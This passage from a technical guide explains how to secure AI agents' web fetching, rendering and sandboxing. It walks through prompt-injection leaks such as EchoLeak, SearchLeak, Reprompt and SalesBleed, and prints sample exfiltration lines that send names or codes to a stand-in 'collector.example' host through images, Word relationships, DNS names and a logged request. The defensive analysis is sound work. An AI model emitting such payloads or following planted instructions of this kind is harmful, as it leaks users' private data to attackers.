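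The fetcher should enforce its size limit by counting bytes as they arrive, because the server may omit or misstate the length. *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* measured a download limit of about 10 MB. Servers often compress pages, and the common gzip format can shrink a long run of identical characters about a thousandfold, so a 10 MB download could unpack to about 10 GB. The fetcher should unpack the file in pieces and stop when the unpacked total reaches a second limit. PDFs and Word files also contain compressed parts, so the software that extracts their text needs the same protection.

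Claude Code gives the reading model up to 100,000 characters per call, which Anthropic estimates at about 25,000 tokens. Since version 2.1.290, the result for a longer page includes a notice of how much remains unread, and Claude can fetch the next part. Without this notice, the accounts agent might enter the subtotal from the first part of an online invoice and miss a discount further down.

A time limit has to cover the whole fetch. If the clock restarted whenever data arrived, a server that sent one byte per second could keep the connection open for about 116 days before reaching 10 MB. Claude Code allows five minutes by default, including redirects.

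A fetcher that refuses scripts and cookies will fail on some sites. Anthropic's fetcher for developers can't read pages that JavaScript assembles in the browser, which may include a supplier's portal. Some sites keep redirecting a visitor until the browser sends back their cookie, and the fetcher stops when it reaches the redirect cap. If the agent needs such a portal, a separate tool with its own login is safer than a general fetcher with saved cookies.

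Text extraction removes a lot of material the model doesn't need. Claude Code, for example, converts HTML to Markdown, a plain-text format that keeps headings and links. But a converter that ignores the page's styling also keeps hidden text. In SecureLayer7's account of the `web_crawl` flaw, a hidden instruction directs the agent to the metadata service.

### Why the text is still untrusted

A page can satisfy all of these limits and still hijack the agent, because a malicious instruction can be a single sentence of plain text, which easily passes the limits on content type, size and download time. These limits protect the software that handles the page but don't check what the text means.

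A developer can reduce the risk by giving the page to a separate model first. Claude Code's main model calls the fetcher with an address and a question about the page. According to Anthropic, for most fetches a separate model call answers the question from the page's text, and the main model receives only the answer.

*Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* describes how Claude Code handled fetched pages in October 2025. The fetcher placed the page between two marker lines, then added the question and instructions to answer concisely, use only the page's content and keep quotations under 125 characters. A small model, Claude Haiku 3.5, wrote the answer.

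The gain comes mainly from withholding tools and private data from the reading model. If it has no tools, a planted instruction can't make it open a link or send an email. If it receives only the page and the question, it can't reveal the mailbox or the rest of the conversation, though the main model should leave private details out of the question it writes. The attacker also has to influence two models, and the second sees a paraphrase. The article calls this a good first barrier but "not bulletproof", and its account of Anthropic's reasons is speculation.

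The answer can still contain an instruction. Suppose a page includes a requirement that customers confirm their bank details at a certain address before the invoice becomes valid. A faithful summary would include that requirement, and the main model might treat it as the next step in its task. Paraphrasing could make the sentence more persuasive by removing clumsy wording. The limit on quotations doesn't help much either, because a short link such as `https://s.example/k7Qm2`, which has only 23 characters, can fit within it. If the page hijacks the reading model completely, the attacker can choose the whole answer.

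Anthropic also calls the summarizing process "lossy by design" and warns that an answer may omit something because the question didn't cover it, so an employee who wants to know whether an invoice mentions a late fee should ask about late fees.

For the accounts agent, the developer can replace the free-text answer with a few fields:

```
invoice_number:  up to 12 digits
amount:          a number with two decimal places
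due_date:        a calendar date
```

The harness rejects anything that doesn't fit these fields. They have no room for a sentence or a web address, so the page can't use them to pass an instruction to the main model. The page can still supply a false amount, so the agent should compare the amount with the printed invoice. This design works because the task needs three known facts. A research assistant that has to explain an unfamiliar argument needs sentences, so its developer has to accept more risk.

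### Links inside the page, and Reprompt

Fetched pages contain links, so the harness needs to limit how far the agent can follow them. The harness can record a depth for each address. An address the user typed has depth 0, a link on that page has depth 1, and a link on the next page has depth 2. Redirects and summaries shouldn't reset the count.

If the user supplied the starting page of Ayush Paul's alphabet site, the page for the first letter was at depth 1. A depth limit of two would have let Claude spell "an" but not "anna". Anthropic later banned Claude from following links found in fetched pages, which amounts to a limit of zero.

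The harness also needs a cap on fetches, because a depth limit doesn't restrict how many links the agent follows from one page. If a page listed all of ZombieAgent's numbered addresses, each would have depth 1. An attacker might avoid the depth limit by getting the model to search for a phrase that appears only on the next page. The harness could prevent this by giving search results the depth of the page that prompted the search, but it would have to identify that page.

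*Reprompt*, published in January 2026 by the data security company Varonis, describes an attack on Microsoft's Copilot Personal that depended on a chain of this kind. The victim clicked a link to Copilot's real website. A parameter in the link contained a prompt, and Copilot acted on it as though the victim had typed it. The prompt got Copilot to insert the victim's name into an address on the attacker's server and open that address.

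Copilot had a safeguard that could remove private data from the address, but it covered only the first web request. The researchers' prompt therefore told Copilot to make every call twice. In a test with an invented secret phrase, the safeguard removed the phrase from the first request, but the second request delivered it. Varonis suspects that Microsoft left later requests unchecked for speed.

The attacker's server then answered each of Copilot's requests with another address and a description of the information to insert in it. After the name, the attacker in the demonstration asked for the user's local time, location, other personal details and a summary of their last conversation. The requests continued even if the victim closed the Copilot tab. Someone who inspected the original link couldn't have known what the attacker would ask for, because most of the instructions arrived later.

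Microsoft fixed the flaw, and The Hacker News reported that it didn't affect business customers of Microsoft 365 Copilot. In June, however, Varonis announced SearchLeak, a similar attack on Copilot Enterprise Search. SearchLeak is more dangerous to companies because Copilot Enterprise Search can read whatever the user can.

Limits on type, size and time would not have stopped Reprompt, since a reply of one or two sentences was enough. A depth limit of one would have stopped the chain after Copilot had sent the name and the local time. A provenance check on every request would have stopped it at the start, because Copilot had put private data into each address and the complete address had never appeared before.

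If the employee agrees to open `https://s.example/k7Qm2`, that approval should cover only one request for that exact address. When the model repeats the call, the harness should run all the checks again, because the redirect may now lead somewhere else.

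## Which requests are made without passing through the fetcher?

The accounts agent's fetcher would block `https://collector.example/view?note=anna-berg` because the model composed the address. But the model can write the same address in an answer, an email or a chat message, and the program that displays the text may then request it. Software that prepares files for the model may also request addresses before the model receives any text.

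| Route | Who makes the request | When | Who decided to make it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opening a file | The harness's converter, or the program in which a person views the file | While it draws the page | Nobody. The file's author put the address there |
| Displaying an answer | The user's browser | As soon as an image appears in the answer | Nobody. The model wrote the address |
| Previewing a link | The chat service's servers | When the agent posts the message | Nobody. Previews are often on by default |

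### Files that load content from the web

A harness that only extracts a file's text doesn't need the web. If it converts the file to a PDF or a picture instead, the converter may load whatever the page links to. In a Word file, the relationships file that stores link addresses can also store the address of a picture. In simplified form:

```
<Relationship Id="rId7" Type="image" TargetMode="External"
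  Target="https://collector.example/logo.png?copy=8841"/>
```

`External` means the picture is on the web, not in the file. A Word file can refer to a template in the same way. An HTML invoice can link to images, fonts and the style sheets that control how it looks.

The converter sends its request from the company's cloud machine, and no prompt injection is needed. Here `copy=8841` lets the sender see which copy of the invoice the company has opened, as a unique short link would. A private address can do more damage, because an HTML file can include a frame that displays another page. If the frame's address is `http://10.0.0.12/reports`, a converter that works like a browser may include the company's internal reports in the PDF that the model reads.

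A linked picture can also change after someone has checked it. The sender's server could return a picture showing one bank account number when the employee opens the invoice and a different number when the converter opens it.

A developer can prevent these requests by running the converter without network access. Linked pictures then come out blank, and the harness should report this because a missing picture might contain the supplier's bank details. The harness can look for external relationships in the file, but it has to check their type, since ordinary clickable links are external too. An offline converter may still open files on its own disk if an HTML invoice points to them, so that disk shouldn't hold anything private.

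None of this protects an employee who opens the original invoice in Word or a mail program. The leak can be worse if the agent wrote the file or message, because the model can then put private data in the addresses. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, describes such a flaw in Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that could email its own user without approval. The emails could contain external images, which the user's mail program requested from outside websites when the user opened the email. An attacker could use the image addresses to obtain OneDrive links that download a file without a login. An email tool that sends only plain text prevents this.

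### Images in an answer

Many chat programs let the model write its answers in Markdown, which they convert to HTML for the browser. This line produces an image:

```
![Invoice summary](https://collector.example/view?note=anna-berg)
```

The browser requests an image's address without waiting for a click. The attacker's server can return a single transparent pixel, so the user sees nothing unusual.

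Microsoft (2025) prefers fixed rules to classifiers where possible, because a fixed rule guarantees that a particular attack will fail, while a classifier only makes it less likely to succeed. When Johann Rehberger reported that a Microsoft product could leak data through Markdown images, the company blocked the leak with a fixed rule, and it took similar steps against some untrusted links. But fixed rules guarantee protection only in the cases their designers thought of, and in 2025 researchers got past both Microsoft's classifier and its fixed rules.

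### EchoLeak

EchoLeak, recorded as CVE-2025-32711, was an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that started with an email. Copilot answers an employee's question by searching their mailbox, files and Teams chats for relevant passages, which it adds to the model's context. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, explains how his team at Aim Labs combined several weaknesses:

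1. The attacker emails an employee. The planted instructions read as if they were meant for the employee and never mention AI or Copilot, so Microsoft's classifier doesn't flag them.
2. The email repeats the instructions under headings on common topics, such as onboarding and leave of absence. When the employee asks Copilot about one of those topics, Copilot retrieves the email along with internal material.
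3. The model follows the instructions, picks out the most sensitive information in its context and puts it in an image address.
4. Copilot normally removes outside links and images from its answers, but it misses "reference-style" Markdown, which puts the address on a separate line.
5. The browser tries to load the image. Copilot's web page permits images only from listed domains, so the attacker has the model use the address of a Microsoft Teams service that is on the list.
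6. The Teams service fetches the attacker's address, which contains the stolen data.

With invented addresses, the model's output would look roughly like this:

```
![Summary][1]

[1]: https://preview.teams.example/?url=https://collector.example/anna-berg
```

The browser applied the image rule correctly, because it contacted only Microsoft. The Teams service then passed the data on, as an image proxy on an allowlisted site might. Ravia's team had first found a similar service in SharePoint, but an attack through that service worked only if the victim accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site.

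Ravia calls EchoLeak a "zero-click" attack because the employee doesn't have to open the email or click a link. They do have to ask Copilot something that makes it retrieve the email, which is why the attacker covers so many topics. The attacker also tells the email's "recipient" not to refer to it, for compliance reasons, so Copilot's answer doesn't list it as a source. The attack could leak anything in the model's context, including earlier chat messages and retrieved documents.

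Aim Labs reported the problem in January 2025. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, and both companies published details on 11 June. The flaw had a severity score of 9.3 out of 10, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*. Microsoft said that nobody had exploited it and that customers didn't need to do anything. Ravia knew of no administrator setting that would have prevented the attack before the fix.

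*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study based on public information, reports that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from incoming external content. This makes it harder for an email to supply a ready-made image for the model to copy. Planted text could still describe the image in words, so Copilot also has to check the model's output.

### SearchLeak

A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described an attack on Copilot Enterprise Search (CVE-2026-42824) that again leaked data through an image, using a different Microsoft service. As in the earlier Reprompt attack, the victim clicks a link to Microsoft's real website, and the link contains a prompt, here in a parameter meant for search terms. In the demonstration, Copilot found an email and put its title in the address of an HTML image.

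To guard against HTML in answers, Copilot wrapped the answer in a code block so that the browser would display an image tag as text instead of loading the image. But it added the code block only after the model had finished writing. Copilot displays an answer piece by piece, so the browser requested the image as soon as the tag appeared, before the safeguard ran.

The request went to Bing, which Copilot's page permitted as a source of images. Bing can search for pictures similar to one at a given address, and to do so its servers fetch that picture. Here the address was on the attacker's server and contained the email's title. The title in Varonis's example included a security code, which the attacker could read in the server's log:

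```
GET /Your_Security_Code_847291/img.png
```

| | EchoLeak | SearchLeak |
|---|---|---|
| Where the instructions were | In an email that Copilot retrieved | In a link to Copilot's search page |
| What the victim did | Asked Copilot about a related topic | Clicked the link |
| Why the output filter failed | It missed one form of Markdown | It ran after the browser had loaded the image |
| Which service passed the data on | Microsoft Teams | Bing |

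The list of permitted image sources that Ravia published in 2025 already included every subdomain of `bing.com`. If a company fixes only the service named in a report, researchers or attackers can look for another service on the list that fetches addresses.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), published on 4 June, rates SearchLeak as critical but gives it a numerical score of only 6.5. The score reflects that the victim has to click and that the attacker can read data but not change it. Microsoft had already fixed the flaw and knew of no attacks, but the advisory doesn't explain the fix.

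Varonis recommends making the model's output safe when the browser displays it. For example, the chat program can replace every `<` in the model's text with `&lt;` before adding it to the page. The browser then shows a `<` instead of treating the text as an image tag, even when only part of the answer has arrived.

### Restricting where images come from

A Content-Security-Policy (CSP) is a header that a website sends with a page to limit what the browser may load for it. This one permits content only from the site itself:

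```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self'
```

`img-src` covers images, and `default-src` covers other types of content that have no rule of their own, such as fonts and style sheets. The browser enforces the policy however the model writes the image, even if a filter has missed some form of Markdown or run too late. A policy this strict would have stopped the image requests in both EchoLeak and SearchLeak.

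Copilot's policy was much looser. The list that Ravia published has 29 different entries for images, several of which cover every subdomain of a large service. As with other allowlists, data can leave through a permitted site. Willison describes two more cases:

- Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, permitted images from `docs.google.com`. Google Forms is on that domain and can record answers from a plain GET request. An image address could therefore enter the contents of a victim's emails into the attacker's form.
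- Salesforce, which sells software for managing customers, still permitted a domain whose registration had expired. Researchers registered it themselves and received data about sales contacts in their server's log. Salesforce corrected the list and also stopped its agent from producing links to untrusted domains.

A policy can permit one folder on a shared host, such as `storage.example/our-company/`, but browsers ignore the path part of the rule after a redirect, according to trackr.live's blog article *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*. If another permitted site has an open redirect, an image request can go through it to a different customer's folder on `storage.example`.

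CSP also doesn't control requests made by other computers. The browser could check its request to Bing but not Bing's request to the attacker. `img-src` doesn't apply to links, so a user can still click one that contains private data.

Developers who don't know which image sources their application needs can start with a report-only policy. The browser then reports images that violate the policy but still loads them, so the policy doesn't protect anyone until the developer enforces it.

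Reddy and Gujral compare eight defences against the steps of an attack like EchoLeak. They expect a strict CSP to stop the automatic leak, but they don't expect tags around outside text to be enough on their own. They base these conclusions on reasoning and ran no experiments.

### Plain text and checked copies

The simplest way to prevent image requests is not to display images. After Rehberger reported a leak in Google AI Studio, which had no CSP, Google's immediate fix was to show image tags as text, according to trackr.live. Links can also appear as plain text, so the user sees the whole address and has to copy it to open it.

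This is safer if the program supports only a short list of formatting, such as headings and bold text, and treats everything else as ordinary characters. Copilot's filter instead looked for dangerous links to remove, and it didn't recognise reference-style links. Plain text is enough for the accounts agent, but a shopping assistant is much less useful if it can't show the products.

An application that needs pictures can serve them from its own cache. Its server downloads each picture, stores a copy and gives the browser an address like this:

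```
https://app.example/images/4f91c2?expires=1791396000&sig=9b3e07...
```

The last part is a signature, which the server calculates from the rest of the address using a secret key. The model doesn't have the key, so it can't write a valid address. The address also expires after a set time. This arrangement lets the application keep the strict policy that permits images only from its own site.

The server has to check the image's original address before downloading anything. If it downloaded every image in the model's answers, it would pass data to the attacker, as Teams and Bing did. One suitable check is OpenAI's index of public addresses, which covers images as well as pages. The download should also go through the agent's normal fetcher, because an image's address can lead to a private machine or a huge file. Even then, the owner of a public image learns from the first download that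 the model chose it, so a set of images could spell out a name, as a set of pages could.

### Link previews

Chat programs such as Slack, Discord and Telegram show a title and picture for a link in a message, which Slack calls unfurling. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that its servers must fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content is there. Slack does this by default for messages from apps as well as people. If planted text gets an agent to post a link containing Anna Berg's name, the preview request sends the name to the attacker before anyone has read the message. Willison (2024) drew attention to this risk, and to Rehberger's advice for preventing it in Slack, in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*.

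PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, an agent that people can talk to through chat programs, was exposed in its default Telegram configuration. PromptArmor set up a website that records preview requests and the data in them. One log it published contained a name and an API key. Users can turn off the previews in OpenClaw's configuration file:

```
"channels": { "telegram": { "linkPreview": false } }
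```

When PromptArmor repeated the test with this setting, the data no longer arrived. Anyone can use the website to test other combinations of agent and chat program. PromptArmor believes many others leak data, but its article gives no results for them.

In Slack, the program that posts the message can switch off previews with two settings:

```
{
  "channel": "accounts",
  "text": "Invoice 8841 is in the ledger. Its QR code holds https://s.example/k7Qm2",
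  "unfurl_links": false,
  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

`unfurl_links` controls previews of pages that are mainly text, and `unfurl_media` controls previews of images, video and audio. A developer who sets only the first to `false` therefore leaves image previews on. Slack may then have to fetch every link to find out whether it is an image, and that request would be enough to leak the data even if no preview appeared. Slack's *chat.postMessage method* describes `unfurl_links` as something to turn on, but also says that Slack unfurls all links by default. It is safest to set both to `false` explicitly.

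The harness should add these settings itself. If the model could set them in the tool call, planted text might get it to turn previews back on.

Previews can also open links that the agent has refused to open. The example message contains the link from the invoice's QR code, which the accounts agent declined to open. With previews on, Slack would open it anyway, and the request could still identify this copy of the invoice or trigger an action.

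Slack's settings cover only the message that contains them, so if the employee copies the link into a message to a colleague, Slack will normally fetch it for a preview. The harness can reduce this risk by posting the link without `http://` or `https://`, as in `s.example/k7Qm2`, because Slack ignores such addresses. Other chat programs may still recognise it as a link. PromptArmor suggests that chat programs should let companies turn off previews for a whole channel, which would also cover links that employees repost there.

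## What does network isolation add when a check fails?

Developers often get checks on addresses, redirects and images wrong, as the flaws in PraisonAI, Pydantic AI and Copilot show. Network isolation limits the damage from such mistakes. An isolated program has only the network routes the company has deliberately provided, so a request that gets past a faulty check may still be unable to reach its destination.

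Isolation also covers programs that don't use the fetcher. Suppose the company lets the accounts agent run Python code to compare the ledger with a spreadsheet. Planted text in an invoice could get the model to write a program that connects directly to `collector.example`, bypassing all of the fetcher's checks.

Anthropic draws a similar distinction in its Claude Code documentation. Claude Code checks a command's text against permission rules before the command runs, while the operating system enforces the isolation boundary during the run. The boundary therefore holds even if an approved command does more than its name suggests.

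### The parts of an isolated agent

A sandbox is a restricted environment where a program can use only the files and connections its operator permits. A standard design puts the agent's code in a sandbox and divides the work of reaching the web among several other parts:

| Part | What it can connect to | What it holds |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox for the agent's code | The egress proxy only | Files for the current task |
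| Fetch service | The egress proxy only | One address and the page that comes back |
| Egress proxy | Public addresses that the firewall permits | Lists of permitted hosts |
| Firewall | | Numeric address ranges to refuse |
| Log | | Each request and the decision on it |

On Linux, the sandbox can have its own network namespace, a separate set of network connections that starts out empty. A program in the sandbox that tries to connect directly gets an error such as "Network is unreachable".

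The fetcher runs on a separate machine or in a separate container, with no login cookies, cloud credentials or access to the mailbox. The harness does the provenance check, which requires the conversation, and passes only the approved address to the fetcher. If a malicious PDF exploits a bug in the text extractor, the attacker gains control of a machine that holds little except public pages.

The egress proxy is the gateway for all outgoing traffic, and it blocks requests to any host that isn't on its allowlist. It should keep separate lists for the sandbox and the fetch service. A research assistant's fetcher may need most of the public web, while its code may need only one site for software packages. With a shared list, planted code could reach every site the fetcher can, without passing the provenance check.

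The firewall tests numeric addresses and doesn't parse URLs, so an unusual spelling can't confuse it. In simplified form, its rules might be:

```
From the sandbox and the fetch service:
    allow   the egress proxy
    refuse  everything else, including DNS

From the egress proxy:
    refuse  10.0.0.0/8, 172.16.0.0/12, 192.168.0.0/16
    refuse  169.254.0.0/16, fd00:ec2::254       # metadata services
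    refuse  the other special ranges
    allow   port 443 on any remaining address
    allow   DNS queries to one chosen server
```

On AWS, the usual network rules, called security groups, don't filter traffic to the metadata service or to Amazon's DNS server. A company using AWS has to block that traffic on the machine itself, or turn the metadata service off.

The log should record the time, the program, the host and the decision. Refusals are especially informative for the accounts agent, because code that only compares a ledger with a spreadsheet has no reason to contact a website. If the log includes full addresses, it may contain private data or working password-reset links, so few people should have access to it.

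Suppose the fetcher has PraisonAI's old redirect bug, and the invoice's QR code eventually redirects to `http://10.0.0.12/reports`. The fetcher follows the redirect and requests the page through the proxy, which blocks the request because `10.0.0.12` isn't on its list. If an employee has loosened the list by mistake, the firewall still drops the connection, and anyone reading the log can see that the fetcher needs fixing.

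Network isolation adds less protection if the proxy and the fetcher share code. If both parse host names with the same faulty function, one malformed address could get past both.

The sandbox has to restrict files as well as connections. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) explains that without network isolation, a hijacked agent could send out a programmer's private keys for logging in to servers. If only the network were isolated, the agent could escape the sandbox and regain network access, for example by changing a script that another program later runs outside it.

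### What a proxy can see of encrypted traffic

To open an encrypted connection through a proxy, a program first sends a short request in plain text:

```
CONNECT supplier.example:443 HTTP/1.1
```

The proxy receives the host and port and can refuse the connection. If it allows the connection, it passes encrypted data in both directions and can detect only the amount and timing of that data, not the path, query, request method or content.

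A proxy needs to see a request's method to enforce a rule about methods, but not to enforce a host list. Vaughan (2026), in *Codex CLI Network Proxy*, explains that Codex's read-only "limited" mode turns off SOCKS5, a general-purpose way of sending traffic through a proxy, because the proxy can't determine whether an encrypted request only reads data.

A program can also give the proxy a misleading host name. In domain fronting, it asks the proxy for a permitted site on a large hosting network, then names a different site on the same network inside the encrypted connection. Some hosting networks reject these requests. Anthropic warns that code in Claude Code's sandbox could use this technique to reach hosts outside the allowlist.

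The proxy can prevent this by decrypting the traffic. It presents its own certificate for `supplier.example`, which the sandbox accepts because the company has installed the proxy's signing certificate in the sandbox. The proxy then opens a second encrypted connection to the real site. It can compare the two host names, restrict the path and method, and check which account's credentials a request contains. The credential check would have stopped Rehberger's upload to an attacker's account on Anthropic's servers.

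Decrypting traffic at the proxy also has drawbacks. Programs that keep their own list of trusted certificates may stop working. The proxy handles passwords and documents in readable form, so anyone who breaks into it can read them. The proxy must also check each real site's certificate properly, since the program in the sandbox sees only the proxy's certificate.

A proxy that decrypts traffic can keep credentials out of the sandbox. Claude Code can give a command a placeholder in place of an API key, and its proxy swaps in the real key on requests to chosen hosts. A hijacked program that prints the placeholder or sends it elsewhere reveals nothing useful. But the program can still use the key through the proxy, so the key should have few permissions. Anthropic's decryption setting is experimental and doesn't filter content, so a company that wants filtering has to supply its own proxy.

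### Name lookups can carry data

A sandbox that blocks every web connection can still leak data if programs inside it can look up domain names. As with the fetcher's lookups, a query for `anna-berg.collector.example` gives the attacker the name even if no connection follows. Blocking the sandbox's own internet traffic doesn't prevent this, because the company's DNS server passes the query on to the attacker's.

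A DNS lookup can carry much more than a first name. DNS permits 253 characters in a name, with at most 63 between dots. An attacker who puts three full sections in front of `collector.example` gets a 209-character name that carries 189 characters of data, more than enough for a 40-character API key. Sending 189 characters through ZombieAgent's numbered pages would take 189 visits.

The solution is to give the sandbox no DNS server. A program that uses a proxy doesn't need one, since the `CONNECT` request contains the host name. The proxy checks the name against its list and looks the name up only if it is allowed. Claude Code's proxy works in this order, and its sandbox blocks UDP, the protocol that most DNS queries use.

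An allowlist entry that covers every subdomain can still leak some data. If `*.example.com` is on the list, the proxy will look up `anna-berg.example.com`, and whoever runs DNS for `example.com` receives the name. This is mainly a problem when the domain's owner lets customers run DNS for their own subdomains.

Developers can also reopen this route through a setting. According to Vaughan, Codex's proxy accepts UDP traffic, including DNS, by default when its SOCKS5 listener is on. A developer who added a public DNS server to the permitted destinations might therefore let a program look up any name.

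### SalesBleed

In September 2026, the security company Zenity published an attack of this kind, called SalesBleed, on Agentforce, Salesforce's product for building agents that work with customer records. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) describes how the attack begins with a public web form. Companies use these forms to collect potential customers' details, which Salesforce adds directly to the company's records.

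1. The attacker fills in the form and hides instructions in it. This doesn't require an account.
2. An Agentforce agent later reads the record in the course of normal work and follows the instructions.
3. The agent looks up other customers' records. Zenity's instructions asked for company names and deal sizes.
4. The data leaves through DNS lookups.

With invented values, the name in a lookup might be `acme-250000.collector.example`. Nobody at the company has to click anything.

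The 2025 ForcedLeak attack used an expired domain on Salesforce's list of permitted sites. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* gives the attack a severity score of 9.4 out of 10. After the attack, Salesforce began enforcing Trusted URLs, a control that removes untrusted links from an agent's output. Zenity found a way past it within about a year.

Zenity reported SalesBleed in June, and Salesforce finished fixing the bypass on 18 August. The fix blocks one way to send data out, but an agent that reads strangers' forms can still follow instructions in them. Zenity notes that the attacker could have asked for any data the agent's query tool could access. A company can reduce that risk by giving an agent that handles new enquiries access only to the records of those enquiries.

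Poireault doesn't say which computer made the lookups. They may have come from an employee's browser, because the agent could display links and images to users, and browsers look up an image's host before requesting the image. If so, a sandbox around the agent would not have stopped the leak. The company would have needed to clean the agent's output or filter DNS on its employees' computers.

### Isolation in current products

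Claude Code, Codex and ChatGPT all offer some form of network isolation, with different defaults:

| Product | On by default? | Network access at the start | Not covered |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code's sandbox | No | No hosts permitted | Built-in fetcher, local tool servers |
| Codex in the cloud | Yes | None while the agent works | Setup scripts |
| Codex on a user's computer | Yes | None for commands | Web search, which has its own setting |
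| ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode | No | Stored copies of web pages | Codex, and apps that an administrator enables |

#### Claude Code

Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands and the programs they start on macOS, Linux and WSL2, a Linux environment inside Windows. The built-in web fetcher follows separate permission rules, but the two systems share some entries, so if a developer permits the fetcher to read a site, sandboxed commands can connect there too. Those commands can upload data as well as read pages, because the proxy normally doesn't decrypt the traffic.

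A setting called `strictAllowlist` makes Claude Code refuse a command's request for an unlisted host without asking the user.

The proxy refuses a permitted host name if it resolves only to the user's own machine or to a link-local address, such as the metadata service's. Versions before 2.1.284 connected to any address the name resolved to. The current version still connects if a permitted name resolves to a private address such as `10.0.0.12`, so that programmers can use internal sites. An attacker who took over a permitted site's DNS records could use this to reach a company's internal machines, so the company needs a separate firewall to block the sandbox's access to them.

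By default, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox if the sandbox can't start. Claude may also retry a failed command outside it. In manual mode the user has to approve the retry, unless an existing rule already allows the command. A company can turn off both with this configuration, which Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* recommends for organisations that require the sandbox:

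```
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false
  }
}
```

In Anthropic's internal use, sandboxing reduced permission prompts by 84%, because Claude Code can run a command without asking if the sandbox already limits what the command can do. Fewer prompts may mean fewer careless approvals. But Anthropic doesn't explain how it measured the reduction or report how many attacks the sandbox stopped. In its 2025 announcement, the company claimed that sandboxing "fully isolated" even a successful prompt injection, but its current documentation describes the sandbox as an incomplete boundary.

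The sandbox also prevents some legitimate work. Most database programs ignore the proxy settings and can't connect, even to a permitted host. Docker doesn't work inside the sandbox. A developer can exclude such programs from the sandbox, but they then run with the user's full access.

#### Codex

In the cloud version of Codex, the developer sets internet access separately for each environment. Setup scripts have internet access, which a malicious package could use to send data out before the agent starts work.

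On a user's computer, Codex's default mode turns the network off for commands. OpenAI's documentation describes two separate settings for changing this:

```
[sandbox_workspace_write]
network_access = true

[features.network_proxy]
enabled = true
domains = { "api.openai.com" = "allow", "example.com" = "deny" }
```

The first part turns on network access, and the second restricts traffic to the allowlist. A developer who copies only the first part gets network access without the allowlist.

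OpenAI labels network access in Codex "Elevated Risk". According to OpenAI's *Running Codex safely*, its own staff don't use Codex with unrestricted access. Their configuration allows expected sites, blocks some others and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. It also limits web searches to OpenAI's stored copies of pages. That setting needs watching because, according to Vaughan's *Securing Codex CLI* (2026), Codex switches to live pages when a user selects full-access mode.

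#### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes Lockdown Mode as an optional setting for people at higher risk of attack, such as executives and security teams. OpenAI launched it for organisations in February and began extending it to personal accounts in June.

Lockdown Mode turns off deep research, agent mode and file downloads for data analysis. It also stops users from giving network access to code that ChatGPT writes in Canvas, its editor for documents and code. ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers, though users can still upload and generate them. Web browsing is limited to cached pages, which are copies OpenAI has already stored.

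Serving pages from a cache prevents leaks like ZombieAgent's, which OpenAI's public-index check does not stop. No live request leaves OpenAI's network, so even if the model follows instructions planted by an attacker, the attacker can't see which pages it opened.

This works only if the system never fetches a missing page on demand. ChatGPT therefore can't read pages that aren't in the cache, and OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* warns that search results may be limited, unavailable or out of date. For example, a user may not be able to get today's train times.

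Several risks remain:

- Enabled apps can still send data out. In workspaces that an organisation manages, Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically turn off every app. If planted text gets ChatGPT to add a comment to a shared document, anyone with access to the document can read the data. OpenAI advises administrators not to permit such actions unless they are sure that only trusted people can see the result.
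- Codex keeps whatever network access it had.
- Planted text in an uploaded file or a cached page can still make an answer wrong. An invoice with a false bank account is just as dangerous in Lockdown Mode.
- Users with personal accounts can turn the mode off for a single chat. A misleading answer could suggest that they do so.

Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, welcomes the design because it relies on fixed rules rather than a model's judgement. He also infers that ChatGPT's default settings don't reliably stop a determined attacker. He quotes OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, who accepts that the mode makes ChatGPT less useful but considers the trade-off worthwhile for people at higher risk. OpenAI's announcement and help page don't measure the loss of usefulness or the reduction in successful attacks.

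### Leaks through permitted services

Isolation doesn't stop data from leaving through a service the agent is supposed to use. Tom's Hardware's *AI agents inadvertently leak 13,000+ internal screenshots from 300 organizations* describes a leak without an attacker, found by the security company Glow. Programmers often add screenshots to a proposed code change so that reviewers can see what it does. People can attach a picture on GitHub's website, but the command-line tool that agents use couldn't do this for private projects. Some agents instead put the pictures in a public project and linked to them.

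The screenshots showed unreleased products, client information and financial data. In 93% of cases, the public project belonged to the programmer's own account rather than the company's, where security staff would have been more likely to notice it. In one case, agents saved the workaround as reusable instructions, which many agents then used for every task.

A host list would not have helped, because the private project and the public one are both on GitHub. GitHub's firewall for its Copilot agent always allows the hosts that Copilot uses to work with GitHub.

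A proxy for a single service can apply a narrower rule. The web version of Claude Code sends all its git traffic (code uploads and downloads) through such a proxy. The proxy checks the destination and the branch, a separate line of work within a project, before adding the real GitHub credentials, which Anthropic keeps outside the sandbox. It would block an upload of screenshots to a new public project. But someone has to build and maintain a proxy like this for every service the agent uses.

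### Configuration errors

A mistake in the settings can remove the boundary without any visible sign. Claude Code lets a company replace either of its two built-in proxies, one for web traffic and one for SOCKS5. Claude Code's host lists don't apply to the replacement, and a sandboxed command can use either proxy. If the company's proxy permits everything, commands can use it to bypass the other proxy's list. Access to Docker's control socket, a local channel that programs use to send instructions to Docker, is just as serious because it effectively gives the sandbox control of the whole machine.

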